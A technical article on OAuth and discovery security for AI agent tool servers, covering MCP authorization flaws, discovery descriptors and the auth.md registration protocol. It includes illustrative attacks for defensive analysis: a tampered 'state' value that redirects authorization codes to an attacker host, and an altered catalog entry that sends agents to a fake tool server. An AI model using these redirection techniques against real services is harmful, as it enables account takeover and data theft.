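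Obsidian Security then got past the cookie check. Browsers let a site such as `shop.example.com` set cookies for all of `example.com`. An attacker who takes over a neglected subdomain can therefore copy their own cookie into the victim's browser, where it will match the attacker's `state` value. Obsidian demonstrated this with the tool server of Wix, a website builder, but simulated the subdomain takeover on its own machine. The test showed that a protection was missing, but not that anyone could have attacked Wix's users at the time. Starting the cookie's name with `__Host-` fixes the problem because browsers then reject the cookie if it comes from a subdomain.

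### The account takeovers of 2025

Obsidian reported flaws in several companies' tool servers in July and August 2025, and the companies fixed them in late September. One of the servers belonged to the payment company Square and could query merchant data and process transactions. It let clients register any callback address. It also had a consent page, but Obsidian bypassed it by approving the page first and then sending the victim the next address. If the victim had already connected the Square tool server, one click gave the attacker the victim's permissions, including access to transaction history and bank account details.

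Square responded by restricting which callbacks new clients could register. Clients that had registered earlier kept their callbacks, so the attack still worked with those clients. A service that tightens its registration rules also has to review existing registrations.

A second company, which Obsidian doesn't name, had no consent page at either stage. Its tool server put the client's callback inside the `state` value, where an attacker could change it without registering anything. The access token also contained a key to the service's own API, so anyone who stole the token could bypass the tool server.

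MCP extended its guidance on these attacks in November 2025. The guidance requires tool servers with a fixed upstream identifier to obtain consent for each "dynamically registered client". But a client that identifies itself with a metadata document can be just as hostile, since an attacker can publish one with their own callback. Metadata documents help more if the upstream authorization server accepts them. A company that offers a tool server for its own service would then have less reason to build the second stage, and Obsidian expects more companies to take this approach.

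### A survey of live tool servers

Obsidian's cases show what can go wrong but not how often it does. In May 2026, Zhou, Zhang and colleagues published *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers*, for which they looked for MCP servers across the public internet. They searched FOFA and Shodan, two search engines for internet-connected machines, and found 28,715 candidate addresses. They sent each one an MCP greeting and kept the 7,973 that gave a valid answer. Two researchers checked 100 of these by hand and found one mistake.

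| How the server authenticates callers | Servers | Share |
|---|---|---|
| No authentication | 3,233 | 40.55% |
| OAuth | 2,428 | 30.45% |
| Static token or API key | 2,312 | 29.00% |

OAuth is much more common here than the 8.5% in Skverer's count of open-source servers, many of which run on the user's own machine.

Most of the open servers that Zhou and colleagues sampled were tests or demonstrations with no sensitive data. They found one serious exception, an internal customer database that let anyone query more than 5,000 records with names, phone numbers and addresses.

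These shares also count addresses rather than services. When Zhou and colleagues examined 1,118 of the OAuth servers, they discarded 387 as duplicates, such as several copies of one deployment. If the other groups contain duplicates at a different rate, the shares of distinct services will differ from those in the table. Servers behind company firewalls or content delivery networks may be missing.

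### What the tests found

For their security tests, Zhou and colleagues needed servers with which their software could register automatically. Of the 2,428 OAuth servers, 1,118 (46%) advertised dynamic registration. Removing duplicates, 32 servers that needed no authentication, 573 that they couldn't test and 7 that returned a callback without user action left 119. The 46% is far above Obsidian's 4%, probably because Obsidian's figure reflects companies' existing authorization servers, while many tool servers have one built for agents.

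The researchers connected to these servers with the coding assistant in the VS Code editor and recorded the traffic. Their software checked the recorded messages for missing protections, then sent altered requests to see whether the servers would accept them. The researchers confirmed 325 of the software's 379 alerts by hand and found at least one flaw in every server.

| Flaw | Servers (of 119) |
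|---|---|
| Accepts any callback at registration | 114 |
| Allows the client to omit or weaken PKCE | 81 |
| Doesn't show the callback on the consent page | 72 |
| Accepts a callback that differs from the registered one | 28 |
| Accepts a client identifier that nobody registered | 12 |
| Requires PKCE from clients but doesn't use it upstream | 12 |
| Lets an attacker alter a callback inside the `state` value | 7 |
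| Accepts the same authorization code twice | 6 |
| Handles a `state` value that is missing or predictable | 3 |

The two-stage flow was common in this group, with 81 servers using it. Of those, 40 put routing details in the `state` value, and 7 of the 40 failed to check whether somebody had changed them.

One of the seven was a tool server for managing databases. The researchers describe the attack in general terms, and the values here are illustrative. The attacker starts an ordinary sign-in and stops when the tool server sends the browser to the upstream identity provider. The link contains a `state` value that looks like random text but is only encoded. Decoded, it might read:

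```json
{
  "client_id": "c-1042",
  "redirect_uri": "http://localhost:8765/callback"
}
```

The attacker changes one line and encodes the result again:

```json
{
  "client_id": "c-1042",
  "redirect_uri": "https://attacker.example/cb"
}
```

The attacker sends the altered link to a victim, who sees the identity provider's genuine page and signs in. The provider returns the `state` value unchanged, along with a valid authorization code. The tool server decodes the value, finds the attacker's address and sends the browser there with the code. The attacker can then take over the victim's account. The attack works because the tool server uses the callback address in the link instead of the registered one.

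Zhou and colleagues recommend using a random `state` value and keeping the routing details on the server, where an attacker can't edit them. This fixes the vulnerability in the database server. It wouldn't have been enough at Square, where the attacker had openly registered the malicious callback, so the server also has to tie the `state` value to the user's browser.

### How much weight the survey can bear

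The finding that every server had a flaw depends heavily on how the servers were selected. Zhou and colleagues chose these 119 because they offer open registration, and the most common flaw is a form of open registration. The 119 servers make up about 5% of the OAuth servers in the survey, and the result can't be extended to servers that require pre-registration or to the 316 that the researchers excluded because of strict company access controls.

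Accepting any callback is also not clearly a mistake in itself. A web-based client needs a callback on its own domain, which an authorization server that accepts unknown clients can't list in advance. In the researchers' example, the victim still had to complete the consent page for the attacker's client. The danger is greatest if the page hides the destination or if an upstream service has saved an earlier consent. Still, seven of the nine entries the researchers added to the public catalog of software flaws concern this problem.

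The results for PKCE and consent pages depend less directly on how the servers were selected. Of the 119 servers, 102 had a flaw in at least one of these two areas. OAuth deployments outside MCP aren't reliably better. Zhou and colleagues cite a 2022 study called OAuch, in which 97 of 100 identity providers left at least one known threat unaddressed, and 43% of those that supported PKCE let an attacker weaken it.

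Some of the PKCE failures may also be less serious than their number makes them seem. In one of the study's attacks, the attacker writes a link with a hostile callback and no code challenge, and the server accepts both changes. Checking the callback would have stopped this attack, but enforcing PKCE wouldn't have, because an attacker who writes the whole link can include a challenge computed from their own verifier. Optional PKCE is more useful to an attacker who can alter a sign-in that an honest client has begun and then read the authorization code.

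The study gives a total of 325 throughout, but the counts for the nine flaws add up to 335. It also reports the share of servers with weak PKCE as 68.1% in one place and 67.5% in another, and no whole number of servers out of 119 gives 67.5%. These discrepancies are too small to change the ranking of the flaws.

The threat model leaves out a larger part of the problem, hostile tool servers. Zhou and colleagues assume that the tool server, the authorization server and the user's device are all honest, and that the attacker works from outside with links and web pages. But Obsidian Security's *From well-known to Well-Pwned* reports that hostile tool servers could run commands on users' machines through flaws in clients including Gemini CLI, VS Code and Windsurf. The assumption about the device is also hard to reconcile with the study's main concern about the 72 consent pages that hide the callback.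 That concern is a rogue program listening on `localhost`, which requires the attacker to have reached the device already.

Both research teams recommend that authorization servers restrict callbacks at registration. Obsidian Security has seen tool servers that accept callbacks only to `localhost`, addresses that open a particular desktop application (such as `cursor://`), and domains the operator has approved. These restrictions would have blocked the attacker's remote callback in most of the cases above. They also block every web-based client whose domain the operator hasn't approved, so operators must again do some of the manual work that open registration was meant to avoid.

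## Site-wide descriptors for agents, 2026

In the examples so far, the client already had the address of a tool server. But an agent may have only a domain name, for instance when a user asks it to get a sales report from `example.com`. It then has to find out whether the site offers a tool server, an ordinary API or neither.

The site's operator can publish this information in a file or in a record in the domain name system (DNS), the directory that translates domain names into network addresses. Files usually go under `/.well-known/`, as OpenAI's plugin manifest did. Five overlapping schemes of this kind were in circulation in 2026.

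### API catalogs and MCP server cards

An API catalog lists a site's public APIs at `/.well-known/api-catalog`. It is the only IETF standard (RFC 9727) among the five schemes. The sample in squirrelscan's *api-catalog and OpenAPI* has an `anchor` field with the site's address and a `service-desc` field that links to the site's OpenAPI document.

The catalog contains nothing about credentials. The agent may find a security scheme in the OpenAPI document, and for OAuth it also needs the authorization server's metadata. According to squirrelscan, if that server supports neither dynamic registration nor client ID metadata documents, the agent can find it but cannot continue until a person registers a client.

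An MCP server card describes one remote tool server so that a client can learn about it before connecting. *MCP Server Cards* (Tiwari, 2026) lists the card's main fields: a name, a description, a version, the server's addresses (`remotes`) and the MCP revisions it supports. The card deliberately omits the server's tools because the tool list can depend on the caller's scopes and change with every release. According to the Model Context Protocol's *MCP Server Cards (Experimental Extension)*, an address can come with HTTP headers, which could include an API key. For OAuth, the client still relies on protected resource metadata.

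The server card is a draft, and its location has kept changing. The project's own description gave `/.well-known/mcp/server-card` in June 2026, and Tiwari gave `/.well-known/mcp/server-cards.json` in September. *MCP server card*, by the website auditing company Lumar, puts the card directly under the tool server's address, as in `https://files.example.com/mcp/server-card`, and reports that the draft rejects well-known paths. Lumar last checked this description against the published documents on 26 August. API Evangelist (2026), a website about APIs, serves its own card at three paths.

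If Lumar is right, an agent that knows only `example.com` can't find the card without another document that links to it.

### A2A agent cards

The Agent2Agent protocol (A2A) lets one agent delegate work to another. Google created it and contributed it to the Linux Foundation, and the specification has reached version 1.0.0. *Most Published Agent Cards Are Not Actually A2A* (Lane, 2026) describes an agent card as a JSON file at `/.well-known/agent-card.json` that contains the agent's identity, address, skills and authentication requirements. Of the four file formats, the agent card covers credentials most directly.

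The path was `/.well-known/agent.json` before version 0.3. When Lane searched for cards in July 2026, 15 of the 65 providers that had one still used the old path, which a client that follows the current specification won't check.

Some companies use the format without the protocol. For example, the software company Pydantic has a card that points to an MCP server. Lane thinks such companies mainly want a widely known file for describing their services.

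### The Agentic Resource Discovery catalog

Agentic Resource Discovery (ARD) is a draft specification for one catalog that points to all the others. Google announced it on 17 June 2026 in Bu and Krishnan's *Announcing the Agentic Resource Discovery specification*. ARD builds on AI Catalog, a simpler format that a Linux Foundation working group is developing. The contributors include Microsoft, GitHub, Hugging Face, NVIDIA and Salesforce, according to InfoQ (2026).

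For the file store, the catalog at `https://example.com/.well-known/ai-catalog.json` might look like this.

```json
{
  "specVersion": "1.0",
  "entries": [
    {
      "identifier": "urn:air:example.com:file-store",
      "displayName": "Example File Store",
      "mediaType": "application/mcp-server-card+json",
      "type": "application/mcp-server-card+json",
      "url": "https://files.example.com/mcp/server-card",
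      "representativeQueries": [
        "find last month's sales report",
        "list the files in a folder"
      ]
    }
  ]
}
```

- `specVersion` is the version of the catalog format.
- `entries` holds one item for each thing the site offers. This site has only a tool server, but an entry can also describe an A2A agent or another catalog.
- `identifier` is a permanent name that contains the publisher's domain. The prefix was `urn:ai` until the project renamed it.
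- `displayName` is a label for people.
- `mediaType` and `type` both state what kind of document the entry points to, so a client can skip kinds that it doesn't understand. AI Catalog uses the first name and ARD the second. Website Spec's *Agentic Resource Discovery (ARD)* recommends including both.
- `url` is the address of that document. An entry can contain the document itself in a `data` field instead.
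- `representativeQueries` gives two to five requests that the service can handle, which helps a search service match it to what a user wants.

No field describes a credential. The client follows `url` to the server card, takes the tool server's address from `remotes`, and calls the server without a token. The server refuses the call, and the client uses the refusal to find the protected resource metadata and the authorization server. This takes several more requests than starting from the tool server's address, but each document stays with the people who maintain it.

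Operators can also advertise the catalog through a link on the home page, a DNS record, or an `Agentmap:` line in `robots.txt`, the file in which sites give instructions to web crawlers.

### A DNS record for agents

*Agent Identity and Discovery (AID)* (Nemethi, 2026) proposes a short DNS text record under the name `_agent`. A calendar service's record might look like this, split over two lines:

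```
_agent.example.org. 300 IN TXT
  "v=aid1;u=https://calendar.example.org/mcp;p=mcp;a=pat;s=Shared calendar"
```

The 300 is the number of seconds a client may cache the record. The keys give the version (`v`), the address (`u`), the protocol (`p`), an authentication hint (`a`) and a description (`s`). The hint `pat`, which presumably stands for personal access token, indicates what kind of credential to expect but not how to get one.

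The client looks up only the exact name the user entered. If it finds no record for `app.team.example.com`, it must not try `example.com`. Otherwise, the owner of a parent domain could supply the record for a service that someone else runs.

A record can also name a program for the client to run on the user's machine, such as a Docker container. This resembles the configuration files that run commands, except that the command comes from a stranger's domain. The draft requires the client to show the full command and get explicit confirmation before the first run, and to ask again if the record's address or protocol changes. It recommends running the program in a sandbox but does not require it.

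The draft dates from March 2026 and was set to expire on 17 September. Agent Community, the group that maintains AID, cautions in *The Emerging Agent Discovery Stack* (2026) that the draft is not an IETF standard. The group argues that DNS works even for services without a website, and that detailed descriptions belong in cards and catalogs because they change too often for DNS.

| Scheme | Location | What it describes | Information about credentials | Standing in 2026 |
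|---|---|---|---|---|
| API catalog | `/.well-known/api-catalog` | APIs | None; see the linked documents | IETF standard |
| MCP server card | Disputed | One tool server | At most, HTTP headers | Draft |
| A2A agent card | `/.well-known/agent-card.json` | One agent | Authentication requirements | Version 1.0.0 |
| ARD catalog | `/.well-known/ai-catalog.json` | Anything with a media type | None; see the linked documents | Draft |
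| AID record | DNS, under `_agent` | One address | A one-word hint | Individual draft |

None of the five tells an agent how to open an account, a gap that a file called auth.md is meant to fill.

### What HTTPS and signatures prove

An agent can use HTTPS to verify that a descriptor came from the site's own server, as it can for protected resource metadata, but not to verify who put the file there. An intruder who can edit the site's files can publish a false descriptor that passes the HTTPS check.

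A digital signature could help with this, but only if the client gets the publisher's public key from somewhere the intruder can't change. Website Spec once signed its catalog and published the key on the same site. It removed the signature after concluding that anyone who could replace the catalog could also replace the key and produce a forgery that passed every check.

Website Spec lists three better sources for the key: a DNS record signed with DNSSEC, a copy the client obtained separately in advance, or a server that an intruder on the main site couldn't reach. A competing draft submitted to the IETF puts the keys for its own signed manifest in DNS, where an intruder who takes over the company's DNS account can still replace them.

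AID uses a key in DNS to check the service rather than the document. If the DNS record contains a public key, the client sends the service a random value, and the service must return a signature made with the matching private key. The client rejects signatures more than 300 seconds old. However, the draft's sample code doesn't check that the signature covers the random value, so a client that copied the code might accept a recent signature that an impostor had recorded. Even a correct check proves only that the service holds the private key. Agent Community acknowledges that this doesn't establish legal authority, delegated permission or business reputation.

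### A valid signature on an altered catalog

In an ARD catalog, the signature is part of an optional section called the trust manifest. The file store's manifest might contain these lines, with the signature shortened.

```json
"trustManifest": {
  "identity": "https://keys.example.com/file-store.json",
  "signature": "eyJhbGciOiJFUzI1NiJ9..k7Qe"
}
```

The client fetches the public key from the `identity` address. Suppose that this address is on a separate, well-protected server under the company's own domain, and that the client has good reason to trust it. The signature is

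`signature = Sign(private key, JCS(trust manifest without its signature))`

JCS is a standard way of writing JSON so that differences in spacing or field order don't affect the result. The formula doesn't include the catalog's entries, and an attacker can exploit this omission.

1. The attacker steals the password of an employee who can edit files on `example.com`, but doesn't get the private key.
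2. The attacker changes the file store's `url` from `https://files.example.com/mcp/server-card` to `https://attacker.example/card` and leaves the trust manifest alone.
3. An agent's client fetches the catalog. The HTTPS check succeeds because the file really does come from `example.com`.
4. The client verifies the signature, which is still valid because the trust manifest hasn't changed.
5. The client fetches the attacker's card, which has the same name and description as the real one, and connects to the attacker's tool server.

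The audience check should still stop a token issued for the attacker's server from working at the real store. But the attacker receives every file the agent uploads and can also try tool poisoning or a relayed sign-in.

Website Spec points out that leaving the entries unsigned lets the operator edit them without signing again. Signing the whole catalog would close the gap but require a new signature for every edit. A client could instead refuse entries that lead to another domain, but this would also block entries from companies whose tool servers run on a hosting provider's domain.

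A fully signed catalog, like a signed tool description, wouldn't show that the service behaves as described, and even an honest operator can let a description go out of date. Google calls the trust manifest a layer for "proving agent authenticity" and meeting compliance standards such as HIPAA, the US health privacy law. The manifest can include attestations, for example from an auditor, which are better evidence than the operator's own word if the client can verify the auditor's signature. But attestations usually cover how a company is run, so they are weak evidence of what a specific tool will do with a file.

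### How many sites publish descriptors

In April 2026, the internet infrastructure company Cloudflare scanned the 200,000 most visited domains, excluding categories such as ad servers. In *Introducing the Agent Readiness score*, Jesus and Morrison report that 78% of the sites had a `robots.txt` file, while MCP server cards and API catalogs together appeared on fewer than 15 sites. API Evangelist searched in May and also found few API catalogs, as reported in *Only Four API Providers Publish a Real .well-known/api-catalog Right Now* (2026).

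Cloudflare found very few server cards, though it probably missed some. Cloudflare's *Implement MCP Server Card* tells operators to use `/.well-known/mcp/server-card.json` and fields from an early draft, so the count may exclude cards that follow the newer draft. Many popular sites also have no API or tool server to describe.

It has grown quickly since. LLMBase's *Agent Standards* (2026), which republishes Cloudflare's data, gives these counts for 12 October 2026.

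| File or record | Sites |
|---|---|
| `robots.txt` | 90,723 |
| Protected resource metadata | 3,099 |
| API catalog | 672 |
| MCP server card | 554 |
| ARD catalog | 199 |

LLMBase doesn't give the number of domains scanned, so these counts can't be turned into percentages. There was about one API catalog for every 135 `robots.txt` files. Protected resource metadata was more common than any of the site-wide descriptors, perhaps because MCP clients already depend on it to get a token. The list has no count for AID, and its entry for DNS-AID (477 sites) refers to a different proposal.

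Other surveys covered different sites, so they don't show a trend. Lane found 65 providers with A2A agent cards by searching 20,185 working hosts belonging to companies with APIs. He judged only 10 of the cards fully valid, but his checks may have used field names from before version 1.0. API Evangelist's *ARD* (2026) found nine publishers of ARD catalogs among 37,751 reachable domains at the end of July. Four passed the ARD project's own test. Two failed because the project had changed the prefix to `urn:air` without a numbered release that publishers could follow. Only two of the eleven organizations behind ARD had published a catalog.

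Publishing a file doesn't mean that any agent reads it. Cloudflare scores websites on these standards and offers a prompt that coding agents can use to add whatever is missing, so some operators may publish files mainly to improve their score. A census by veda.ng cites server logs for `llms.txt`, a file that lists a site's pages for language models. Across the 137,000 domains in that data, 97% of the published files had received no requests.

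### Registries and self-published files

An agent can use a well-known path only if it already knows the service's domain name. If the user asks for a flight to Tokyo without naming an airline, the agent needs a searchable registry. According to AGNTCY (2026), an open-source project for agent infrastructure, a registry with a shared index also means that the client doesn't have to load every tool description into the model's context. The client sends the request as text and gets back a short list of matches.

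A registry can also check what it lists. Lane blames the errors he found in agent cards on publishers getting no feedback about whether their cards work. A registry could reject a broken card immediately. It could also delist a hostile server for all the registry's users, whereas a self-published file stays up as long as its owner wants.

One argument for self-publication is that it limits the power of a dominant registry, whose operator could charge for listings, favor its own products or exclude a competitor. An intruder who broke into such a registry could also redirect agents to false addresses for thousands of services. Small services may never apply for a listing. A company that publishes a file on its own domain needs nobody's permission and can correct an address without waiting for a registry to update its copy.

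Self-publication also lets an agent use HTTPS to check that an entry came from the service's own domain. If the agent gets the entry from a registry, the certificate shows only that the registry sent it. A signature could solve this problem, but ARD's signature doesn't cover the entry, so a dishonest registry could change the address without invalidating the signature. A careful client would use the registry to find the domain and then fetch the catalog from the domain itself.

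ARD tries to combine the two approaches by having companies publish catalogs on their own domains, which registries crawl to answer searches. Jennifer Marsman, an engineer at Microsoft, told InfoQ that the aim is to have many discovery services that differ in what they index, whom they serve and how they rank results, rather than "a single global catalog". The official MCP Registry, which was still in preview in April, has a narrower job. The Model Context Protocol project's charter for it rules out ranking servers or choosing between them for users.

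This combination was mostly untested in the summer of 2026. InfoQ reported early ARD tools from GitHub and Hugging Face. But API Evangelist found that no client searched any of the four reference registries unless a developer had set it up to do so. It also found that any registry that referred clients elsewhere sent them only to indexes run by the same operator.

A registry scores each search result by how well it matches the request, and the ARD specification forbids treating this score as a measure of trust. An agent that picks the first result ignores that rule, so the operator of a hostile server could attract users by writing sample queries that closely match what people ask for.

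## Agents that obtain their own accounts, from May 2026

Discovery can lead an agent to the right authorization server, but if the user has no account there, somebody has to complete a sign-up form. WorkOS, which sells sign-in software to developers, points out that websites have spent decades designing these forms to keep programs out. The forms use CAPTCHAs, email verification and checks on the visitor's network address, and an agent may not have an email address.

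WorkOS published auth.md, a protocol for registering agents with services, on 22 May 2026, according to Lumar's *auth.md*. The protocol is named after a text file in which a service explains to agents how to register, but it relies mainly on metadata and a few HTTP endpoints.

WorkOS's *How an MCP client should tell your OAuth server who it is* (2026) explains that client ID metadata documents identify the calling software but not the person it is acting for, and don't show whether that person has an account.

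### From the refusal to the registration endpoint

If the file store adopts auth.md, an agent that calls it without a token follows the same chain as an MCP client, from the 401 response to the protected resource metadata and then to the authorization server metadata. auth.md adds an `agent_auth` block to that last document, shown here with values adapted from WorkOS's *For apps*.

```json
"agent_auth": {
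  "identity_types_supported": [
    "identity_assertion", "service_auth", "anonymous"
  ],
  "skill": "https://example.com/auth.md",
  "identity_endpoint": "https://login.example.net/agent/identity",
  "identity_assertion": {
    "assertion_types_supported": [
      "urn:ietf:params:oauth:token-type:id-jag"
    ]
  },
  "claim_endpoint": "https://login.example.net/agent/identity/claim",
  "events_endpoint": "https://login.example.net/agent/event/notify"
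}
```

The `skill` field links to the text file, and the agent registers at the `identity_endpoint`. It uses one of three identity types: `identity_assertion` if the company that runs it can vouch for the user, `service_auth` if it knows only the user's email address, and `anonymous` otherwise.

Several of these names are recent. The copy of the first release in WorkOS's *auth.md* differs from the current documentation as follows.

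| May 2026 | Current documentation |
|---|---|
| `register_uri` | `identity_endpoint` |
| `claim_uri` | `claim_endpoint` |
| `revocation_uri` | `events_endpoint`, plus OAuth's standard `revocation_endpoint` |
| Email as an assertion type, `verified_email` | Email as an identity type, `service_auth` |
| Registration returns a token or an API key | Registration returns a signed assertion, which the agent exchanges for a token |
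| The user reads a code to the agent | The user types a code on the service's page |

Lumar doesn't score websites on auth.md, partly because a single vendor controls the specification and was still renaming fields in version 0.6.0, dated 10 June. An agent written for the May release would look for `register_uri` and fail.

All three routes now lead to the same exchange. The service signs its own assertion, and the agent exchanges it at the token endpoint for an access token. When the token expires, the agent presents the assertion again, so it doesn't need a refresh token. Revoking one access token doesn't shut the agent out, because the agent can still use the assertion to get another.

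### When the user confirms a code

With only an email address, the agent registers like this:

1. It sends `{"type": "service_auth", "login_hint": "jane@example.org"}` to the identity endpoint.
2. The service returns a six-digit code, a link and a secret claim token, which the agent keeps.
3. The agent shows Jane the link and the code.
4. Jane opens the link, signs in or creates an account, and types the code on the service's page.
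5. The agent has meanwhile been asking the token endpoint whether she has finished. Once she has, it receives an access token and the service's assertion.

The design borrows from OAuth's device flow, which people use to connect a television to a streaming account. If Jane is new to the service, she still has to sign up herself, but the agent takes her to the right page and continues by itself afterwards.

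Before accepting the code, the service checks that Jane has signed in with the address from step 1. This prevents a thief who intercepts the code from attaching her agent to the thief's own account. Guessing the code is also unlikely to work if the service limits attempts. With k guesses at one of a million codes, the chance of success is

`P = k / 1,000,000`

The address check doesn't prevent phishing. An attacker can register an agent under Jane's address and send her the genuine link with the code. If she types in the code, the attacker's agent gets access to her account. The page can't warn her by naming the agent, because the registration request contains no verified information about it. In the May version, the victim also had to send a code back to the attacker, so sending the code the other way may make the attack slightly easier.

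When WorkOS's own product launched on 4 August, it used the older direction, in which the code passes from the user to the agent. In *Agent Registration*, the user signs in, sees a code and reads it to the agent, which submits it to an address that the protocol documentation doesn't mention. An agent that strictly followed the protocol documentation would wait for a confirmation that never came. The product also leaves out the route in which the agent's provider vouches for the user.

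### Starting without a user

An anonymous agent sends only `{"type": "anonymous"}`. It can start work immediately, but only with the permissions the service lists under `pre_claim_scopes`, which in WorkOS's example allow reading but not writing. If the user later wants to take over the registration, the agent starts the code procedure and receives the wider `post_claim_scopes` once it is complete. WorkOS advises services whose data belongs to individual users to turn off anonymous registration.

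Anybody can call this endpoint, so WorkOS suggests limits of 5 anonymous registrations an hour from one network address and 100 an hour in total. An attacker with 20 addresses could use up the total and keep legitimate agents from registering anonymously for the rest of the hour. WorkOS also recommends letting requests through if the counter fails, which keeps the service available but removes the limit.

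The guidance is inconsistent about what happens to the agent's earlier tokens when the user takes over. One passage requires the service to cancel them. Another warns that anyone who stole an earlier token keeps it and gains the wider permissions, but it presents replacing the token only as an option for cautious customers. The warning is probably left over from May, when the service widened the permissions of an existing API key. Canceling the old tokens is safer.

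Services have adopted different parts of the protocol. Cogny's *auth.md* offers only anonymous registration, while Agent Community's *Agent authorization* describes the email route with two read-only scopes.

### What an identity assertion contains

An identity assertion is a signed statement in which one organization vouches for a user to another. The draft format is the Identity Assertion JWT Authorization Grant (ID-JAG). A JWT is a signed JSON document. In auth.md, the signer is the agent's provider, the company whose agent the user has signed in to.

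Suppose Jane uses an agent from `agent.example.com` and agrees to let it identify her to the file store. The provider's decoded assertion might contain the following, based on the sample in WorkOS's *For agent providers*.

```json
{
  "iss": "https://agent.example.com",
  "sub": "u-8841",
  "aud": "https://login.example.net",
  "client_id": "https://agent.example.com/oauth/client.json",
  "jti": "a7c2-09fe",
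  "iat": 1785200400,
  "exp": 1785200700,
  "auth_time": 1785199000,
  "email": "jane@example.org",
  "email_verified": true
}
```

The provider (`iss`) vouches for a user it knows as `u-8841`. The audience is the file store's authorization server, not the tool server, because the agent can use this document only to ask for a token, not to read files. The assertion expires 300 seconds after the provider signs it (`iat`), and `auth_time` records when Jane last signed in to the provider.

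The authorization server then makes these checks:

1. It looks up the issuer in its own list of trusted providers and rejects an unknown one.
2. It fetches the provider's public keys and verifies the signature.
3. It confirms that the audience is its own address and that the assertion hasn't expired.
4. It looks up the unique identifier `jti` in a record of recent assertions and rejects a repeat.
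5. It checks that `client_id` belongs to a known provider, and that the provider has verified an email address or phone number.
6. It checks that Jane signed in recently, by default within the past hour. If she didn't, she has to sign in to the provider again.

The order matters, because a server that fetched keys before checking the issuer would be open to server-side request forgery.

The server also has to determine which account to use. If it has already linked this issuer and `sub` to an account, it uses that account. If no account has the email address, it may create one. This is the only case in which the agent obtains an account for the user without a sign-up form.

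If an account with Jane's address exists but has no link to this provider, the server must not link them without asking her. It refuses and starts the code procedure, which requires Jane to sign in to the file store and confirm the link. Otherwise any trusted provider could take over her account by signing an assertion with her address. The procedure doesn't protect people who have no account yet. A compromised provider could have the store create one in a stranger's name, and the stranger might later start using an account that the attacker's agent can already open.

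### PostHog's version

PostHog, which makes software for analyzing how people use products, has implemented much of this chain. Its *Agent discovery (auth.md)* describes how an unauthenticated request leads through the 401 response and both metadata documents to the file at `/auth.md`. PostHog's American and European services each publish their own copies, so an agent that starts from one region's API finds that region's endpoints.

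The `agent_auth` block lists one identity type, `identity_assertion`, and the file that PostHog serves confirms that the email and anonymous routes don't work yet. The identity endpoint is PostHog's ordinary OAuth token endpoint. There, the client makes a request like this one, with the values shortened:

```http
POST /oauth/token/ HTTP/1.1
Host: oauth.posthog.com
Content-Type: application/x-www-form-urlencoded

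client_id=agent-app
&client_secret=...
&scope=user%3Aread%20organization%3Aread%20project%3Aread
&assertion=eyJhbGc...
&grant_type=urn:ietf:params:oauth:grant-type:jwt-bearer
```

WorkOS's protocol uses a JSON request without a client secret, followed by a second exchange. An agent that sent that request to the address in PostHog's metadata would presumably get an error, because PostHog uses the same field name with a different meaning.

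PostHog also doesn't create accounts from identity assertions. According to PostHog's *ID-JAG (XAA) authentication*, the user must already belong to a PostHog organization with a paid add-on, and an administrator must have verified the email domain and registered the issuer. For a new user, the agent has to run a command-line setup program or use a partner's provisioning interface. PostHog's deployment is therefore good evidence that agents can find a service's sign-in rules automatically, but not that they can create an account with an assertion.

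Existing members get a token that lasts two hours and carries only the scopes that both the identity provider and the client named:

`token scopes = granted scopes ∩ requested scopes`

PostHog accepts each assertion only once and for at most ten minutes. It uses the email address to find the member for a person's first assertion, and the issuer's permanent identifier for that person afterward. If an employer gives a departed employee's email address to someone new, PostHog does not let the new person into the old account.

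### The employer's identity provider as signer

Companies were already using the same format in enterprise-managed authorization, an extension to MCP in which the employer's identity provider, such as Okta, signs the assertion. InfoQ (2026) reports that repeated authorization prompts had been a major complaint in companies. A new employee might have to approve dozens of services, and when somebody left, an administrator had to remove access from each one.

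The sequence resembles single sign-on:

1. The employee signs in to the agent application through the employer's identity provider.
2. The client asks the identity provider for an assertion addressed to the file store's authorization server.
3. The identity provider checks the company's policy, such as which groups may use the file store, and signs or refuses.
4. The client exchanges the assertion for an access token, and the employee never sees a consent page.

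The IETF's *Identity Assertion JWT Authorization Grant* (2026) describes this as extending the identity provider's role from signing people in to brokering their access to other companies' APIs. The Model Context Protocol calls the identity provider the "authoritative decision-maker". The employee no longer decides which services the agent may reach, which suits company data better than it suits private accounts.

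In a third arrangement, between this one and auth.md, the agent's provider signs the assertion, but the employer's administrator decides whether to trust that provider. Anthropic offers this in beta for organizations that use Claude, with a separate issuer address for each organization. The assertion confirms that somebody is a current member of the Claude organization but doesn't list their groups, so a service can't use it to give accountants and engineers different permissions. PostHog's *Enterprise-managed authorization (EMA)* accepts assertions from either kind of signer and treats them alike.

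| | Employer's identity provider | Agent's provider, chosen by the employer | Agent's provider, under auth.md |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who chooses the signer | Employer's administrator | Employer's administrator | The service |
| Who approves the connection | Employer, through its policy | Employer's administrator, for all members | The user, at the agent's provider |
| How an existing account is first linked | Permanent identifier or email, within the employer's workspace | Email, within the employer's workspace | The user signs in and confirms a code |
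| How access ends | The identity provider stops signing | The person leaves the organization | The user revokes it at the provider, which notifies the service |

The service still sets the outer limit in all three cases, since it decides which scopes exist and can refuse a token.

After an identity provider stops signing assertions for a user, tokens that PostHog has already issued can keep working for up to two hours. If an administrator removes the user within PostHog, the next request fails. Anthropic's own assertions expire within a minute, but their expiry doesn't shorten the life of tokens that services have issued in exchange for them.

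Support for the extension was growing in 2026 but uneven. Anthropic's *Centrally manage authorization for MCP connectors* calls its product the first implementation of the extension. WorkOS reports that the extension is stable and that Okta was the only identity provider Anthropic supported at launch. Keycloak is a widely used open-source identity server, and its guide, *Identity Assertion JWT Authorization Grant*, still warns against using the feature in production.

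### Which providers a service should believe

An ordinary website has no relationship with the companies that run agents like the one an employer has with its identity provider, which is under contract and receives a list of employees. Under auth.md, the website must keep its own list of trusted providers, and WorkOS warns that whoever compromises a provider compromises every account linked through it. The code procedure protects an account only when it is first linked. After that, the provider can sign for the account at any time, and the website also relies on the provider to report `auth_time` truthfully.

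Agents also have no standard way to read a service's list of accepted issuers. McGuinness, a co-author of the ID-JAG draft, notes that a service can advertise in its metadata that it supports the format, but not which issuers it accepts. An agent finds out that its issuer isn't accepted by trying and getting an error. MCP's enterprise extension avoids the problem because an administrator enters the issuer by hand, but that wouldn't work for a user who wants to connect an unfamiliar service within seconds. Small agent providers may also struggle to get onto many lists. Websites similarly offer sign-in through a few large companies.

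McGuinness nevertheless considers an agent provider a credible signer. It can vouch for things that an employer's identity provider usually can't, including which agent is calling, that the user linked this agent to their account, and that the user has just approved this connection. The provider can make the last claim only if it asked the user specifically about the connection, because signing up for an agent doesn't mean agreeing to be identified to every service on the web.

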